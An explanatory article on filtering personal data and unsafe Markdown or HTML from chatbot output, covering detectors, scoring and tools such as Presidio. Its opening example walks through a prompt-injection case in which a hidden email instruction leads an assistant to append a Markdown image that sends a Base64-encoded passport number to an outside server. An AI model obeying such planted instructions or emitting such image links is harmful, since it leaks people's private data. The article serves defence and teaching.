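# Removing personal data and unsafe markup from language model outputs after generation

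## What an output filter removes and where it acts

An output filter is software that inspects the text a language model has produced and masks, replaces, escapes or blocks parts of it. Companies that build chatbots, search assistants and customer-service tools place these filters between the model and whatever receives its answers. A filter may remove identifiers of real people, such as names and phone numbers, and markup (HTML or Markdown) that makes a web browser run a program or send data to an outside server. Both can appear in one answer, as when a line of markup sends a person's data out of a private conversation.

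The filter uses a detector to find content that should be removed, and a separate step to remove or alter it. Residual leakage is any such content that remains in the output or that a reader can still infer.

### An example answer

Suppose that an employee of a travel agency asks an assistant built on a language model to sum up an open case. The assistant searches the agency's files and email, queries the booking system and writes the following answer, in which every detail is invented:

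```
Marta Lindqvist called on Tuesday about a cancelled ferry crossing.
She is a harbour pilot from Visby, aged 58.
Call back on 555-0142 or write to marta.lindqvist@example.com.
The passport number on the booking is X4471902.
Refunds go through form 555-0187.
Payment takes ten working days.
The ferry company has confirmed the cancellation.
![booking status](ADDRESS?d=WDQ0NzE5MDI=)
```

The answer contains four identifiers: the full name, the phone number, the email address and the passport number. An identifier is a piece of text that points to one person by itself. "Harbour pilot", "Visby" and "58" are quasi-identifiers, details that single someone out only in combination. Thousands of people live in Visby, but perhaps only one is a 58-year-old harbour pilot, so a filter can remove all four identifiers and still leave Lindqvist recognisable to a neighbour. Most studies of detectors use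 the label PII (personally identifiable information), which covers identifiers and some quasi-identifiers, but the studies differ on which quasi-identifiers to include.

The last line is a Markdown image. ADDRESS stands for the web address of a server that the agency does not run, and the characters after `d=` are the passport number in Base64, a common way of encoding data as letters and digits. The employee did not ask for an image. The assistant added it because of prompt injection, the practice of placing instructions in content that a model reads, such as a web page or an email, so that the model follows them as if its user had given them. Here, somebody sent the agency an email with hidden instructions for the assistant to end its answer with an image and put any passport number it found in the image's address.

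### The screen, the log and other programs

From the model, the text can go to three places, and a filter protects different people at each.

An output filter keeps Lindqvist's personal data from readers who shouldn't see it and protects the agency and its customers from unsafe markup. These aims call for different settings. The employee needs the phone number to call back, but showing the same number to a stranger would be a leak. Neither reader needs the image. Many chat interfaces display an answer while the model is still writing it, so the filter has to hold back a little text, because it can't recognise "555-" as the start of a phone number until more digits arrive. It also has to run before the browser displays the image, because once the image is displayed, the passport number has already been sent.

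The log is the stored copy of the conversation, which engineers use to find faults and companies use to improve their models. Filtering it protects the people in the conversation when others open the file later. *Meta AI Chatbot Training Exposes User Data to Contractors* (2025), an entry in the OECD's AI incident monitor, reports that contractors Meta hired to review chatbot conversations regularly saw unredacted names and contact details. Fortune (2025) described the case alongside older ones at Amazon and Microsoft, whose contractors had listened to users' voice recordings. Logs can also be exposed by accident. Tech Times' *AI Data Leak Exposes 22.7TB of Files, Including Private Chats* (2026) reports that exposed storage at the service 302.ai held more than 144,000 chat logs with personal information, though nobody confirmed that an intruder had read them. A filter on the screen doesn't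 protect such logs if the system writes them before the filter runs.

The third destination is another program. The agency might feed the answer into its customer database, or let the assistant issue commands to a server. OWASP, a community project that catalogues the security risks of web applications, covers this danger in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*. One of its examples is an application that passes model output straight to a system shell, the part of an operating system that executes typed commands, which lets an attacker run code on the machine. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre's guidance explains that users, and anyone who manages a prompt injection, can influence what the model writes, so a program that trusts the output gives them indirect access to functions they should not control. A filter here protects the operator of the receiving system and everyone whose data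 it holds. It can also cause errors, since a database that expects a phone number will reject "[PHONE]".

### Where the personal data comes from

Much of the personal data in answers comes from the conversation itself, as when a user pastes in a letter and the model repeats the names in it. This does no harm while that user is the only reader, but assistants also write to other people. *Privacy Collapse* (2026) gives an example in which a model had to write to a team leader and ask for a different project. The model had access to stored memory (notes an assistant keeps about a user), which included a divorce, a savings account number and therapy sessions. The original model left these out of the message, but after fine-tuning (further training on a narrower set of examples), it included sensitive details from the memory. Some providers also reserve the right to improve their models with what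 users type, and according to *Large Language Models as Search Engines* (2025), such data can resurface in answers to other users.

Retrieved documents are another source of personal data. When the Gizmodo journalist Matt Novak asked chatbots for Novak's own phone number, one of them searched the web and returned the number of a different Matt Novak in the Los Angeles area. Tool results, the data returned when a model calls another program, can also contain personal data. Programs on the web often send more than the request required. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of web security around language models, discusses this weakness as excessive data exposure. In the example, the employee wanted the state of the case, but the booking system returned the whole passenger record, including Lindqvist's passport number.

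A model may also reproduce personal data from its training text. How often this happens depends on how memorisation is defined, and *The Model's Language Matters* (2025) notes that researchers have proposed many competing definitions. Researchers usually test for memorisation by giving a model part of a training document, or a person's name, and checking whether it produces the correct email address or phone number. Luo, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Do LLMs Really Memorize Personally Identifiable Information?*, argue that this test mistakes guesses for memorisation. For example, a model given the name Marta Lindqvist could guess the part of her email address before the @ sign without having memorised it.

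To separate the two, they measured how much of each target the prompt already contained. They defined this overlap as the length of the longest run of characters shared by the prompt and the target, divided by the length of the target. They tested three mGPT-family models, whose training text is public, in 32 languages. Given the 100 tokens (words or parts of words) that preceded each item in the training text, the largest model reproduced 1.08% of the email addresses and 0.23% of the phone numbers. The average overlap was 0.90 for the email addresses it got right and 0.50 for those it missed. When the researchers counted only cases with an overlap below 0.5, the success rate fell to nearly zero. Many of the phone numbers came from prompts that contained almost the same digits, such as a fax number that differed by one digit.

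The finding suggests that much apparent memorisation is the model completing what the input supplies. It is hard to extend to the much larger models now in use, because the largest model tested had 13 billion parameters and successes grew with size, from 111 email addresses in the smallest model to 527 in the largest. The study also left out data that models learn during fine-tuning.

A model can guess a real person's data without having memorized it, and for that person the correct guess is no better than a memorized value. Luo and colleagues found that, given strong cues, the models could complete real email addresses that were absent from their training text. Even a request for a list of phone numbers, with no other cues, produced some real ones, including 2,074 from the largest model, or 0.28% of what it generated.

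Outside the laboratory, it is often hard to tell which source the personal data came from. *El extraño caso del hombre cuyo número de teléfono la IA no* (Pérez Colomé, 2026) describes Fernando, a Spanish engineer who received at least eight calls and messages between August and October 2026 from people trying to reach a pharmacy, a bicycle shop, a restaurant and other businesses. Where Fernando could trace the mistake, the number had mostly come from Google's Gemini Flash, and once from ChatGPT. It recurred so often that he began to doubt that the models were making it up. In 2025, Meta's assistant on WhatsApp made a similar error when it gave a private person's number to a user who had asked for a train company's contact details (OECD, *Meta AI Chatbot on WhatsApp Leaks Private Phone Number in Privacy Breach*, 2025).

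These cases are hard for any filter to handle. The users asked for a business's phone number, and the assistant gave them a phone number. A filter that removes every phone number would make the assistant useless for such questions, and one that allows business numbers would have let Fernando's through, since nothing in the text marks it as private.

### Images, links and scripts

Markdown is a plain-text format that John Gruber created in 2004 with help from Aaron Swartz, on the model of the formatting habits people had developed in email, as the specification project CommonMark describes it. Chatbots commonly write in it. The application then converts the text into HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser turns the HTML into what the user sees. This last step is rendering. Two asterisks on either side of a word become a tag for bold type. Square brackets followed by an address in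 round brackets become a link:

```
[booking status](ADDRESS)    becomes  <a href="ADDRESS">booking status</a>
![booking status](ADDRESS)   becomes  <img src="ADDRESS" alt="booking status">
```

In Markdown, an image differs from a link only by a leading exclamation mark, but the browser treats them very differently. It opens a link only when the user clicks, so a wary reader can check the address first. Images are fetched automatically because the browser needs them to draw the page. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a security researcher's account of how Microsoft's chatbot displayed its answers, describes how the model returns Markdown, the application converts it into an image tag, and the browser contacts the server without any action by the user.

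The request includes the full address, including everything after the question mark. In the example, the outside server therefore receives `WDQ0NzE5MDI=`, and its owner decodes the passport number. This happens even if the server returns no picture or the image is out of view. Under the HTML standard, set out in WHATWG's *Embedded content*, browsers load images immediately, even those far below the visible part of the page, unless the page asks for lazy loading. Sending private data to an outside party without permission is called exfiltration.

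A script can do more than an image, which sends only the one message the model wrote into its address. The script runs as a program inside the page, where it can read other parts of the conversation and send requests in the user's name. Cross-site scripting is an attack in which the attacker gets a page to run their own script. Markdown has no notation for scripts, but it allows raw HTML, which a converter may pass through unchanged. GitHub, which displays Markdown from millions of users, therefore sanitises the HTML after conversion. A sanitiser parses markup and keeps only the elements and attributes considered safe. Because it works on the converted text, it doesn't have to predict what the converter will produce.

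### What a filter can do with a finding

Once the detector has found something, the filter has several ways to act on it, and each costs the reader something different.

| Action | Effect on the example | Cost to the reader |
|---|---|---|
| Mask | "[PHONE]" takes the place of 555-0142 | The employee sees that a number is missing and cannot call back |
| Replace with a surrogate, an invented value of the same type | "Karin Holm" takes the place of Marta Lindqvist | The text reads naturally, but the employee may take the invented name for the real one |
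| Escape, so that the browser shows code as ordinary characters | The image line appears as text and the browser fetches nothing | Clutter on the screen, and no harmless images either |
| Block | A notice takes the place of the whole answer | The employee also loses the refund details |
| Send for review | A colleague decides what to release | Delay, and one more person reads the passport number |

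The right method depends on where the output goes. Surrogates suit a log that engineers will study, because they keep sentences whole and the engineers don't intend to call the people mentioned. On the employee's screen, a mask is better than an invented phone number, which the employee may dial and reach a stranger. Escaping the image tag stops the request but leaves the encoded passport number in the text, where anyone who later opens the log can decode it. A sanitiser that deletes the whole tag solves both problems.

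### Scoring a detector

Researchers score a detector against a text in which people have marked the correct items. The unit is usually the span, a stretch of text that a detector or an annotator marks as one item. If the correct span is "Marta Lindqvist" and the detector marks only "Lindqvist", a strict scoring rule counts a miss and a lenient one counts a success.

Suppose annotators have marked the four identifiers in the example, and a detector marks five spans: the name, the phone number, the email address, "Visby" and the form number 555-0187, which is formatted like a phone number. The first three are correct, and the detector misses the passport number.

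Precision is the share of the detector's findings that are correct, here 3/5 or 0.60. Recall is the share of the items it should have found that it found, here 3/4 or 0.75. F1 is the harmonic mean of the two, 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall), here 2 × 0.60 × 0.75 / 1.35 or 0.67.

The false positive rate uses a different unit, the text. It is the share of texts without the item that the detector flags anyway. If each sentence of the example counts as a text, four of the seven contain no identifier, and the detector flags two of those four (the ones with "Visby" and the form number), so its false positive rate is 50%.

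Many detectors score each candidate and report only those above a threshold. The chosen threshold, called the operating point, sets the trade-off between missed items and false alarms. For example, lowering it might catch a passport number that was previously missed but also wrongly flag "Tuesday" and "58".

| Threshold | Spans marked | Correct | Precision | Recall | F1 | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
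| Higher | 5 | 3 | 0.60 | 0.75 | 0.67 | 50% |
| Lower | 8 | 4 | 0.50 | 1.00 | 0.67 | 50% |

F1 and the false positive rate are the same in both rows, but at the higher threshold the passport number reaches the reader. Recall is usually the first figure to check for a privacy filter, but missing a passport number lowers it no more than missing a first name does.

The one image needs to be counted separately. A personal data detector will probably miss it because `WDQ0NzE5MDI=` does not look like a passport number, so the part of the filter that handles markup has to find it.

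A detector with a low false positive rate can also have poor precision when identifiers are rare. If 20 of 1,000 answers contain an identifier, a detector that flags 15 of those 20 and 2% of the rest raises 15 correct alarms and about 20 false ones, for a precision of about 0.43. If 500 of the 1,000 answers contained an identifier, the same detector would raise 375 correct alarms and 10 false ones, for a precision of 0.97.

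## Pattern-based detection of personal data: how it works and how it scores

Many identifiers have a fixed format. Most payment card numbers have 16 digits, for example, and every email address has an @ sign. A programmer can write patterns for these formats without any training data. A pattern-based detector is a collection of such patterns, with rules for deciding which matches to accept.

### A detector for card numbers

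Suppose that the travel agency's assistant writes this sentence:

```
She paid for order 6011 0009 9013 9425 with card 6011 0009 9013 9424.
```

The card number is one that payment companies publish for testing, so it belongs to nobody. The order number is invented. To find candidates, the detector uses a regular expression, a formula that describes a set of strings:

```
\b(?:\d{4}[ -]?){3}\d{4}\b
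```

Here `\d{4}` stands for four digits and `[ -]?` for an optional space or hyphen. The `{3}` repeats that group three times, and four more digits follow. The `\b` at each end marks the edge of a word, which stops the expression from matching the first 16 digits of a longer number. American Express numbers have 15 digits and need a separate expression.

Both numbers in the sentence match, so the detector needs a second test. Card issuers choose the last digit of a card number so that the whole number satisfies a checksum, an arithmetic test for typing errors that Hans Peter Luhn of IBM devised in the 1950s. Counting from the right, the detector doubles the second digit, the fourth and so on, and subtracts 9 from any result above 9. It then adds these results to the digits it didn't double. The number passes if the total is a multiple of 10.

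```
Digit     6  0  1  1  0  0  0  9  9  0  1  3  9  4  2  4
Doubled  12     2     0     0    18     2    18     4
Counted   3  0  2  1  0  0  0  9  9  0  2  3  9  4  4  4   total 50
```

The card number passes. The order number ends in 5 instead of 4, so its total is 51 and it fails. About one in ten arbitrary 16-digit numbers passes by chance, so the checksum removes about nine in ten of the order and tracking numbers that would otherwise cause false alarms. It catches every single-digit error and every swap of two neighbouring digits except 0 and 9. For example, 6011 0009 0913 9424, which has a 0 and 9 swapped, also adds up to 50.

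A number that fails its checksum can still be sensitive. A customer may have mistyped a real card number, and anyone who knows that one digit is wrong has only 16 corrections to try, one for each position. Pdftools, which sells document software, therefore lets users choose between a strict mode, which discards a match that fails the checksum, and a relaxed mode, which keeps the match but lowers its score by 0.30.

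The score is a number from 0 to 1 for how much to trust a match. For patterns, a programmer usually sets the starting value by hand, and words near the match can raise it. These words matter most for identifiers without a checksum, such as phone numbers. The agency's earlier answer contained a phone number in "Call back on 555-0142" and a form number in the same format in "Refunds go through form 555-0187". Suppose the phone pattern starts at 0.4, a word such as "call" in the same sentence adds 0.2, and the detector reports only matches that score at least 0.5. It then reports the phone number at 0.6 and drops the form number at 0.4. The method fails on "Call 555-0142 or send in form 555-0187", because "call" raises both scores to 0.6.

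Finally, the detector has to resolve overlapping matches. In marta.lindqvist@example.com, an email pattern matches the whole string, a web address pattern matches "example.com", and a name detector may match "marta.lindqvist". If the filter removed only the name, the reader would still see the email domain. A simple rule is to keep the match with the highest score, or the longest match if scores tie. When a pattern and a trained model mark exactly the same span, a setting in Pdftools' *Detection configuration* gives priority to the pattern.

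### Presidio's design

Presidio is a free, open-source toolkit that many studies use as their baseline. Its analyser finds personal data and its anonymiser removes it, according to Microsoft's *Presidio* overview. The analyser runs a set of recognisers, each for one or more types of data. Some use a regular expression, with or without a checksum. Others use a deny list, a fixed list of words to remove; Microsoft's guide for developers gives the example of titles such as "Mr." and "Dr.". According to the same guide, more than 100 milliseconds for a text of 100 tokens is probably too slow.

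No regular expression can describe all names, so Presidio also uses named-entity recognition, the task of marking names of people, places and organisations in text. By default, it uses a trained model from the language-processing library spaCy that classifies each word using the words around it. Presidio's results for names therefore depend on this model, although researchers often describe Presidio as rule-based.

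Each finding has a type, a position and a score. In an example from deepset, whose software can call Presidio, the sentence "Contact Alice at alice@example.com" yields a person with a score of 0.85 and an email address with a score of 1.0. Weak patterns start much lower. Microsoft's tutorial on context gives a starting score of 0.01 to its US postcode pattern, which matches essentially any five digits. Presidio then compares the recogniser's context words with the dictionary form of each word in the sentence, so that "cards" counts as "card", and raises the score if any match.

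Whoever installs the tool sets the threshold. Microsoft's reference pages give a default of 0, at which Presidio returns even a bare five-digit number if the postcode recogniser is active. NVIDIA's toolkit for filtering the input and output of language models uses Presidio with a default of 0.2, and its sample configuration raises this to 0.6. Two products that use Presidio may therefore behave quite differently.

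Microsoft created Presidio, but the repository appears to have moved to another GitHub account in 2026. Microsoft's *Presidio Analyzer package* listing shows that version 2.2.362 of the analyser still came from Microsoft's account, and piwheels' *presidio-anonymizer* page dates the companion release to 15 March. By August, beam's *data-privacy-stack/presidio* profile listed the repository under an account called data-privacy-stack, with 207 contributors and recent changes. The documentation is still at a Microsoft address.

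### Presidio's low score on PIIBench

The lowest published figures for Presidio come from *PIIBench* (Jha, April 2026), which merged ten public datasets into a collection of 2.4 million texts, including invented customer records, Wikipedia sentences, Reuters news and company filings to the US financial regulator. Jha tested eight detectors on a sample of 1,398 texts with 3,383 labelled items. Presidio came first, with an F1 of 0.1385, a precision of 0.152 and a recall of 0.127. The spaCy model on its own had a slightly higher recall, 0.140, but raised many more false alarms.

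| Type | Items in the sample | Presidio's F1 |
|---|---|---|
| Places | 525 | 0.307 |
| People | 437 | 0.264 |
| Dates | 151 | 0.133 |
| Email addresses | 119 | 0.128 |
| Social security numbers | 16 | 0.020 |
| Card numbers | 23 | 0 |
| IP addresses | 80 | 0 |
| Addresses | 91 | 0 |
| Usernames | 109 | 0 |
| Figures in financial reports | 873 | 0 |

Presidio misses seven of every eight items on PIIBench, but its low recall for email addresses is hard to believe, because they have one of the most rigid formats. *GLiNER Guard* (Minko, Sadiekh and Kokuykin, 2026) reports that Presidio's recall for email addresses is 92% in both the legal and the medical texts of SPY, another English test set. PIIBench may have damaged the addresses before the detectors were run. Several of its sources store text as separate words and punctuation marks, and if the test joined these with spaces, "alice @ example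 . com" would no longer match an email pattern.

The scoring rule also lowers the figures. Jha counted a finding as correct only if its start, end and type all matched the label. If a source labels "Marta" and "Lindqvist" as two items and Presidio marks the full name as one, the result is two misses and a false alarm, even though a filter would have masked the whole name.

The ten sources used more than 80 labels, which Jha merged into 48. The merged type for people included ages, heights and eye colours, which no name detector looks for. The type for card numbers included security codes and issuer names. Most invented card numbers would also fail the Luhn checksum, which may be why Presidio found none of them. Some near-duplicate labels remained, such as NAME and PERSON, or STREET_ADDRESS and ADDRESS, so a detector can mark the right words and still get the type wrong.

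Gaps in coverage only partly explain Presidio's low scores. The 873 figures from financial reports, such as revenue and total assets, aren't personal data, and Presidio isn't meant to find them. Removing them from the count would raise its recall only to about 0.17 and its F1 to about 0.16, if the number of false alarms stayed the same.

Jha's explanation is that each detector works only in the field it was made for. The financial model's result casts doubt on this. Its training data came from the same filings that supply those 873 items, yet its recall of 0.021 amounts to about 72 correct findings, at most 8% of the items in its own field. This suggests that the text preparation or the scoring lost many correct findings, for this model and probably for the others. Jha reports no scores under a more lenient rule, so the number lost is unknown. The figure of 0.1385 is best read as a lower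 bound, and it is a poor guide to how much personal data Presidio would leave in a chatbot's answer.

### Sums mistaken for identifiers

Pattern-based detectors can mistake the numbers in mathematics lessons for personal data, and better scoring wouldn't remove this weakness. Zhou, Vanacore and colleagues, in *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring*, studied 1,000 sessions from a US tutoring platform, which had run Presidio with some extra rules of its own before sharing the transcripts. Of the 4,648 messages with redactions, 65% had lost something that wasn't personal data. For example, the platform's filter had cut "9351 / 7 = 1335.8571" short after the decimal point and deleted the 180 from "180/pi". More than 99% of the supposed driving licence numbers were false alarms.

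To build a test set, the researchers had a language model judge each redaction from the surrounding conversation, look for identifiers the platform had missed, and invent replacements for the real ones. Three researchers checked the model's output on 100 transcripts and revised the instructions before running it on the rest. The resulting set, MathEd-PII, has 1,995 labelled items, most of them names. The researchers then ran Presidio on the set again, with added patterns for schools, courses and school years, and compared it with six language models. The table shows Presidio and the two highest-scoring models.

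| Detector | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Presidio | 0.254 | 0.747 | 0.379 |
| Claude 4.5 Opus, plain prompt | 0.911 | 0.730 | 0.810 |
| Claude 4.5 Opus, warned about numbers in maths | 0.905 | 0.720 | 0.802 |
| Claude 4.5 Opus, told which messages are maths | 0.934 | 0.730 | 0.820 |
| Gemini 3 Pro, plain prompt | 0.887 | 0.760 | 0.818 |
| Gemini 3 Pro, warned about numbers in maths | 0.869 | 0.735 | 0.796 |
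| Gemini 3 Pro, told which messages are maths | 0.888 | 0.764 | 0.821 |

The gain came from replacing the patterns with a language model, and it was almost entirely in precision. Zhou and colleagues present the result as a case for prompts that take account of the subject, but both models did about as well with a plain prompt. Presidio and the language models each missed about a quarter of the items. In the maths passages, Presidio found more items than the best Gemini configuration, with a recall of 0.72 against 0.62.

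Most of Presidio's false alarms also came from two recognisers. Of the 4,358 false alarms, the date recogniser produced 3,386, in a test set with three real dates, and the driving licence recogniser produced 344. Switching both off would raise precision to about 0.70 and F1 to about 0.72, while missing at most five more real items. This estimate relies on hindsight because it uses the test results to choose the settings, but anyone who ran Presidio on a few tutoring sessions would notice the same two recognisers raising false alarms.

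The misses had a different cause. Presidio's name model relies on capitals and punctuation, which students often leave out in a chat. In the examples Zhou and colleagues give, Presidio finds the name in "hey Olivia" but not in "hey olivia", and in "Hi Alex," but not in "Hi Alex" without the comma. The true number of misses may be higher than the recall suggests, because the labels started from Presidio's own redactions, and any name that both Presidio and the language model overlooked would not be counted as a miss. MathEd-PII also casts doubt on one of the zeros in PIIBench. Presidio's pattern for IP addresses worked on the tutoring transcripts with no false alarms, although they contain only two addresses.

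### Rules for some types, a model for others

Patterns and models fail on different things, so many filters divide the work between them. Minko and colleagues describe one such hybrid, GLiNER Guard. Its model has 145 to 209 million parameters, depending on the version, and finds names and postal addresses by comparing stretches of text with descriptions of what to look for. Rules find everything with a fixed format. A final step translates the model's labels and joins fragments into complete items.

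The researchers tested this on 1,810 invented Russian texts, which two annotators had checked. They also ran the models without any rules, so their results show where each method is better. The right-hand column gives the best result from five models, three versions of their own and two from an earlier family.

| Type | F1 of the rules | Best F1 of a model alone |
|---|---|---|
| Email addresses | 100 | 100 |
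| Access tokens and recovery keys | 100 | 66.7 |
| Bank card numbers | 95.5 | 69.4 |
| Social insurance numbers | 95.5 | 75.7 |
| Card security codes | 94.7 | 41.1 |
| Taxpayer numbers | 88.0 | 97.2 |
| Phone numbers | 60.4 | 87.2 |
| Passport numbers | 49.6 | 60.6 |

The rules scored between about 95 and 100 on most fixed formats, including three types of business registration number not shown here. They did worse on taxpayer numbers and much worse on phone and passport numbers, and the best model alone beat them on all three. People write phone numbers in many ways, and a Russian passport number is ten digits without a checksum, so it looks like many other numbers. The same gap for phone numbers appears in English texts. On SPY, Presidio found 68% of phone numbers in the legal texts and 66% in the medical ones, while Llama-3-70B, a general language model, found 93% and 90%. A hybrid that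 assigns every number to the rules, as GLiNER Guard does, loses some accuracy on phone numbers.

The complete system's best scores were 75.7 on names and 68.7 on addresses, each from a different version of the model. These scores depend heavily on the step that joins fragments. One version scored 0.5 on addresses when it worked alone, because it marked city, street and flat separately while the test expected a single item. After joining, it scored 65.9. Exact matching can evidently make a fairly useful detector look worthless, which is a reason to be wary of very low scores like those in PIIBench. But joining lowered the largest version's score on names from 83.1 to 52.3. These results all come from tidy synthetic text in one language, and real conversations would probably be harder for both halves of the system.

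A similar division of work between patterns and a model makes sense where computing power is scarce. *Introducing Rampart* (Groot and Coristine, 2026), written for the US government's National Design Studio, presents a tool that runs in the user's browser and removes personal data from a message before it reaches a chatbot. Regular expressions find social security and other ID numbers, and a small language model called MiniLM finds names and street addresses. Rampart filters the user's messages rather than the chatbot's output, but the detection problem is the same.

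### The reach of rules and the case for keeping them

Rules work well for identifiers that an institution issues in a fixed format, especially those with a checksum or a distinctive character such as the @ sign. They are unreliable for bare runs of digits, because only the surrounding words show whether the digits are a phone number or a form number. They are of little use for names and free-form addresses beyond matching fixed lists, and they miss quasi-identifiers such as "harbour pilot" unless someone has listed them. They also cannot distinguish a private person's phone number from a business's, as in Fernando's case.

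Within those limits, rules have advantages that F1 doesn't measure. They need almost no compute, and they give the same result on the same text every time. One DataRobot test fails any model response containing an email address, phone number, social security number, card number or IP address. It uses only regular expressions and, for card numbers, the Luhn checksum. In its documentation, DataRobot describes pattern matching as faster, cheaper and more reliable than a language model for such identifiers, but acknowledges that the test misses names and addresses.

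Engineers can also find out why a rule fired. Presidio can log its decision process, which lets them trace a finding to a particular recogniser and its score. If a tutoring platform's filter is deleting fractions, an engineer can identify the date pattern responsible, correct or disable it, and rerun old transcripts to confirm that nothing else has changed. A neural network has no single line to correct, and retraining it to fix one error may introduce others. A company that has to explain to a regulator or a customer why a passport number got through therefore has a strong reason to keep rules, even alongside a more accurate model. A log that quotes each finding becomes another store of personal data, so it needs care too. DataRobot's test avoids this problem by reporting only the types it found and how many of each.

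## Model-based detection of personal data: how it works and how it scores

Rules can't cover all names, so filters also use detectors trained on texts in which people or other models have marked the personal data. These detectors come in three main kinds. A token classifier gives every token a label, such as "part of a name". A span matcher compares stretches of text with the names of categories, such as "passport number". A generative model, the kind behind chatbots, lists the personal data or copies the text without it.

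### How OpenAI Privacy Filter labels tokens

In April 2026, OpenAI released Privacy Filter, a token classifier that anyone may download, modify and use commercially. In *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter*, de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues (2026) explain how they built and tested it.

The researchers started from a small generative language model, which predicts each token using only the tokens before it. This limits a detector, because in "555-0142 is her home number" the clue follows the number. They removed the restriction so that the model can use up to 128 tokens on either side of each token. They also replaced the output layer, which scored every token in the vocabulary as a possible next token, with one that scores 33 labels. Finally, they trained the converted model on public and synthetic texts with labeled personal data. A model from the GPT-5 family added labels to the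 public texts that lacked them.

Privacy Filter has 1.5 billion parameters but uses only 50 million of them for any one token, because each layer sends a token through four of its 128 subnetworks. It can run on a laptop or in a web browser, and it labels up to 128,000 tokens in one pass. It has eight categories:

| Category | What it covers |
|---|---|
| Person | Names of private people, and usernames that identify them |
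| Address | Places associated with a private person |
| Email | Addresses for personal use or that identify a private person |
| Phone | Numbers associated with a private person |
| Web address | URLs and IP addresses that identify a private person or are meant for a private audience |
| Date | Dates of birth and other dates that identify a private person |
| Account number | Card, bank and other account numbers |
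| Secret | Passwords, access keys and other credentials |

In their tests, the researchers counted passport numbers as account numbers, so Marta Lindqvist's would fall into that category. Neither "harbour pilot" nor her age has a category. Most of the definitions include the word "private", so the model should mask a customer's phone number but leave a shop's alone. No pattern can make that distinction. The model needs a clue in the text to make it, and in Fernando's case there was none.

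Each of the eight categories has four tags. Three mark the beginning, inside and end of an item that spans several tokens, and the fourth marks an item of a single token. With one more label for background text, this makes 8 × 4 + 1 = 33 labels. "Marta Lindqvist" should receive "begin person" and "end person".

### From tags to spans

Suppose the model labels the text "Ask Marta Lindqvist today" and each word is one token, though in practice a surname often takes several. The table gives invented scores for the background label and the four person tags. The other 28 labels score too low to matter.

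| Tag | Ask | Marta | Lindqvist | today |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| O | 4.0 | 1.0 | 2.2 | 4.0 |
| B (begin) | 0 | 3.0 | 0.5 | 0 |
| I (inside) | 0 | 0.2 | 0.4 | 0 |
| E (end) | 0 | 0.1 | 2.0 | 0 |
| S (single) | 0 | 2.5 | 1.0 | 0 |

Choosing the highest score in each column gives O B O O. This sequence is invalid because a name begins at "Marta" and never ends, so it doesn't determine how much text the filter should mask.

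*Constrained Decoding for Computationally Efficient Named Entity Recognition Taggers* (Lester, Pressel and colleagues, 2020) built the rules for tag order into the last step of a detector. Only I or E of the same category can follow B or I, and only O, B or S can follow O, E or S. A text can't start with I or E, or end with B or I.

A Viterbi decoder finds the valid sequence with the highest total. It moves through the text from left to right and, for each possible tag of the current token, keeps only the best valid sequence that ends in that tag. At "Marta", the best sequence ending in B totals 7.0 and the best ending in S totals 6.5. At "Lindqvist", E can follow B, which gives 7.0 + 2.0 = 9.0. O can't follow B, so its best total comes from S, 6.5 + 2.2 = 8.7. The word "today" then adds 4.0 to both.

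```
O B O O   4.0 + 3.0 + 2.2 + 4.0 = 13.2   invalid
O B E O   4.0 + 3.0 + 2.0 + 4.0 = 13.0   masks "Marta Lindqvist"
O S O O   4.0 + 2.5 + 2.2 + 4.0 = 12.7   masks "Marta"
O O O O   4.0 + 1.0 + 2.2 + 4.0 = 11.2   masks nothing
```

The decoder returns O B E O, so the filter masks the whole name. The strong evidence that a name begins at "Marta" outweighs the slight preference for background at "Lindqvist". The method also takes little computation. Four tokens with 33 labels have about 1.2 million possible sequences, but the decoder makes at most 33 × 33 = 1,089 comparisons for each new token.

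Many earlier taggers had an extra layer that learned from the training data which tags may follow which. Lester and colleagues left this layer out and applied the tag-order rules only at decoding, which roughly halved the training time. F1 didn't change significantly on three of four public datasets, and on the fourth it fell from 87.4 to 86.1. The rules only guarantee a well-formed sequence, so they still allow O O O O, which leaves the whole name in the output.

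### Moving the operating point

Privacy Filter's decoder has six adjustable values, called transition biases, that make certain steps in a sequence more or less likely. Software Mansion's *Interface*, a reference page for developers who run the model, lists one each for staying in the background, entering a span, continuing it, ending it, returning to the background, and starting a new span directly after another. The decoder adds the corresponding bias to the sequence's total whenever the sequence takes that step.

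In the example, O B E O never goes from background to background. O S O O does so once and O O O O three times, so a bias for staying in the background changes the winner:

| Bias | O B E O | O S O O | O O O O | What the filter masks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | **13.0** | 12.7 | 11.2 | "Marta Lindqvist" |
| +0.5 | 13.0 | **13.2** | 12.7 | "Marta" |
| +1.0 | 13.0 | 13.7 | **14.2** | Nothing |

Raising this bias reduces false alarms but increases misses, while a positive bias for entering a span does the opposite. For example, Presidio missed the name in the greeting "hey olivia". If the filter scored "olivia" 2.4 as background and 2.0 as a single-token name, it would leave the name in the text when no bias was applied. A bias of +0.5 for entering a span would raise the name score to 2.5, so the filter would mask "olivia", along with any ordinary word whose scores are equally close.

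Biases can also lengthen or shorten a span, which a simple threshold can't do. Engineers should test them on sample texts first, because Software Mansion's note on the bias for entering a span contradicts its general rule about what positive and negative values do.

### Scores on invented texts and on credentials

de Bourcy and colleagues tested Privacy Filter on PII-Masking-300k, a large set of invented texts in six languages, and on CredData, a collection of program code that contains passwords and access keys. They scored both by token and by span.

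| Test | Precision (tokens) | Recall (tokens) | F1 (tokens) | F1 (spans) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PII-Masking-300k | 0.940 | 0.980 | 0.960 | 0.926 |
| PII-Masking-300k, labels corrected | 0.968 | 0.981 | 0.974 | 0.942 |
| CredData | 0.747 | 0.965 | 0.842 | 0.617 |
| CredData, labels corrected | 0.750 | 0.965 | 0.844 | 0.624 |

The correction to PII-Masking-300k covered apparent false alarms, which were spans that Privacy Filter had marked and the dataset had not. GPT-5.4, a reasoning model, reviewed each of these spans and judged about 10,000 to be real personal data that the dataset had left unlabelled. Human reviewers checked 100 of these judgements and agreed with all of them. The researchers also tried to review the apparent misses, but left those labels unchanged because the reviewers agreed with GPT-5.4 only 85% of the time. The corrected score therefore excludes the dataset errors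 found among the false alarms but still includes any among the misses.

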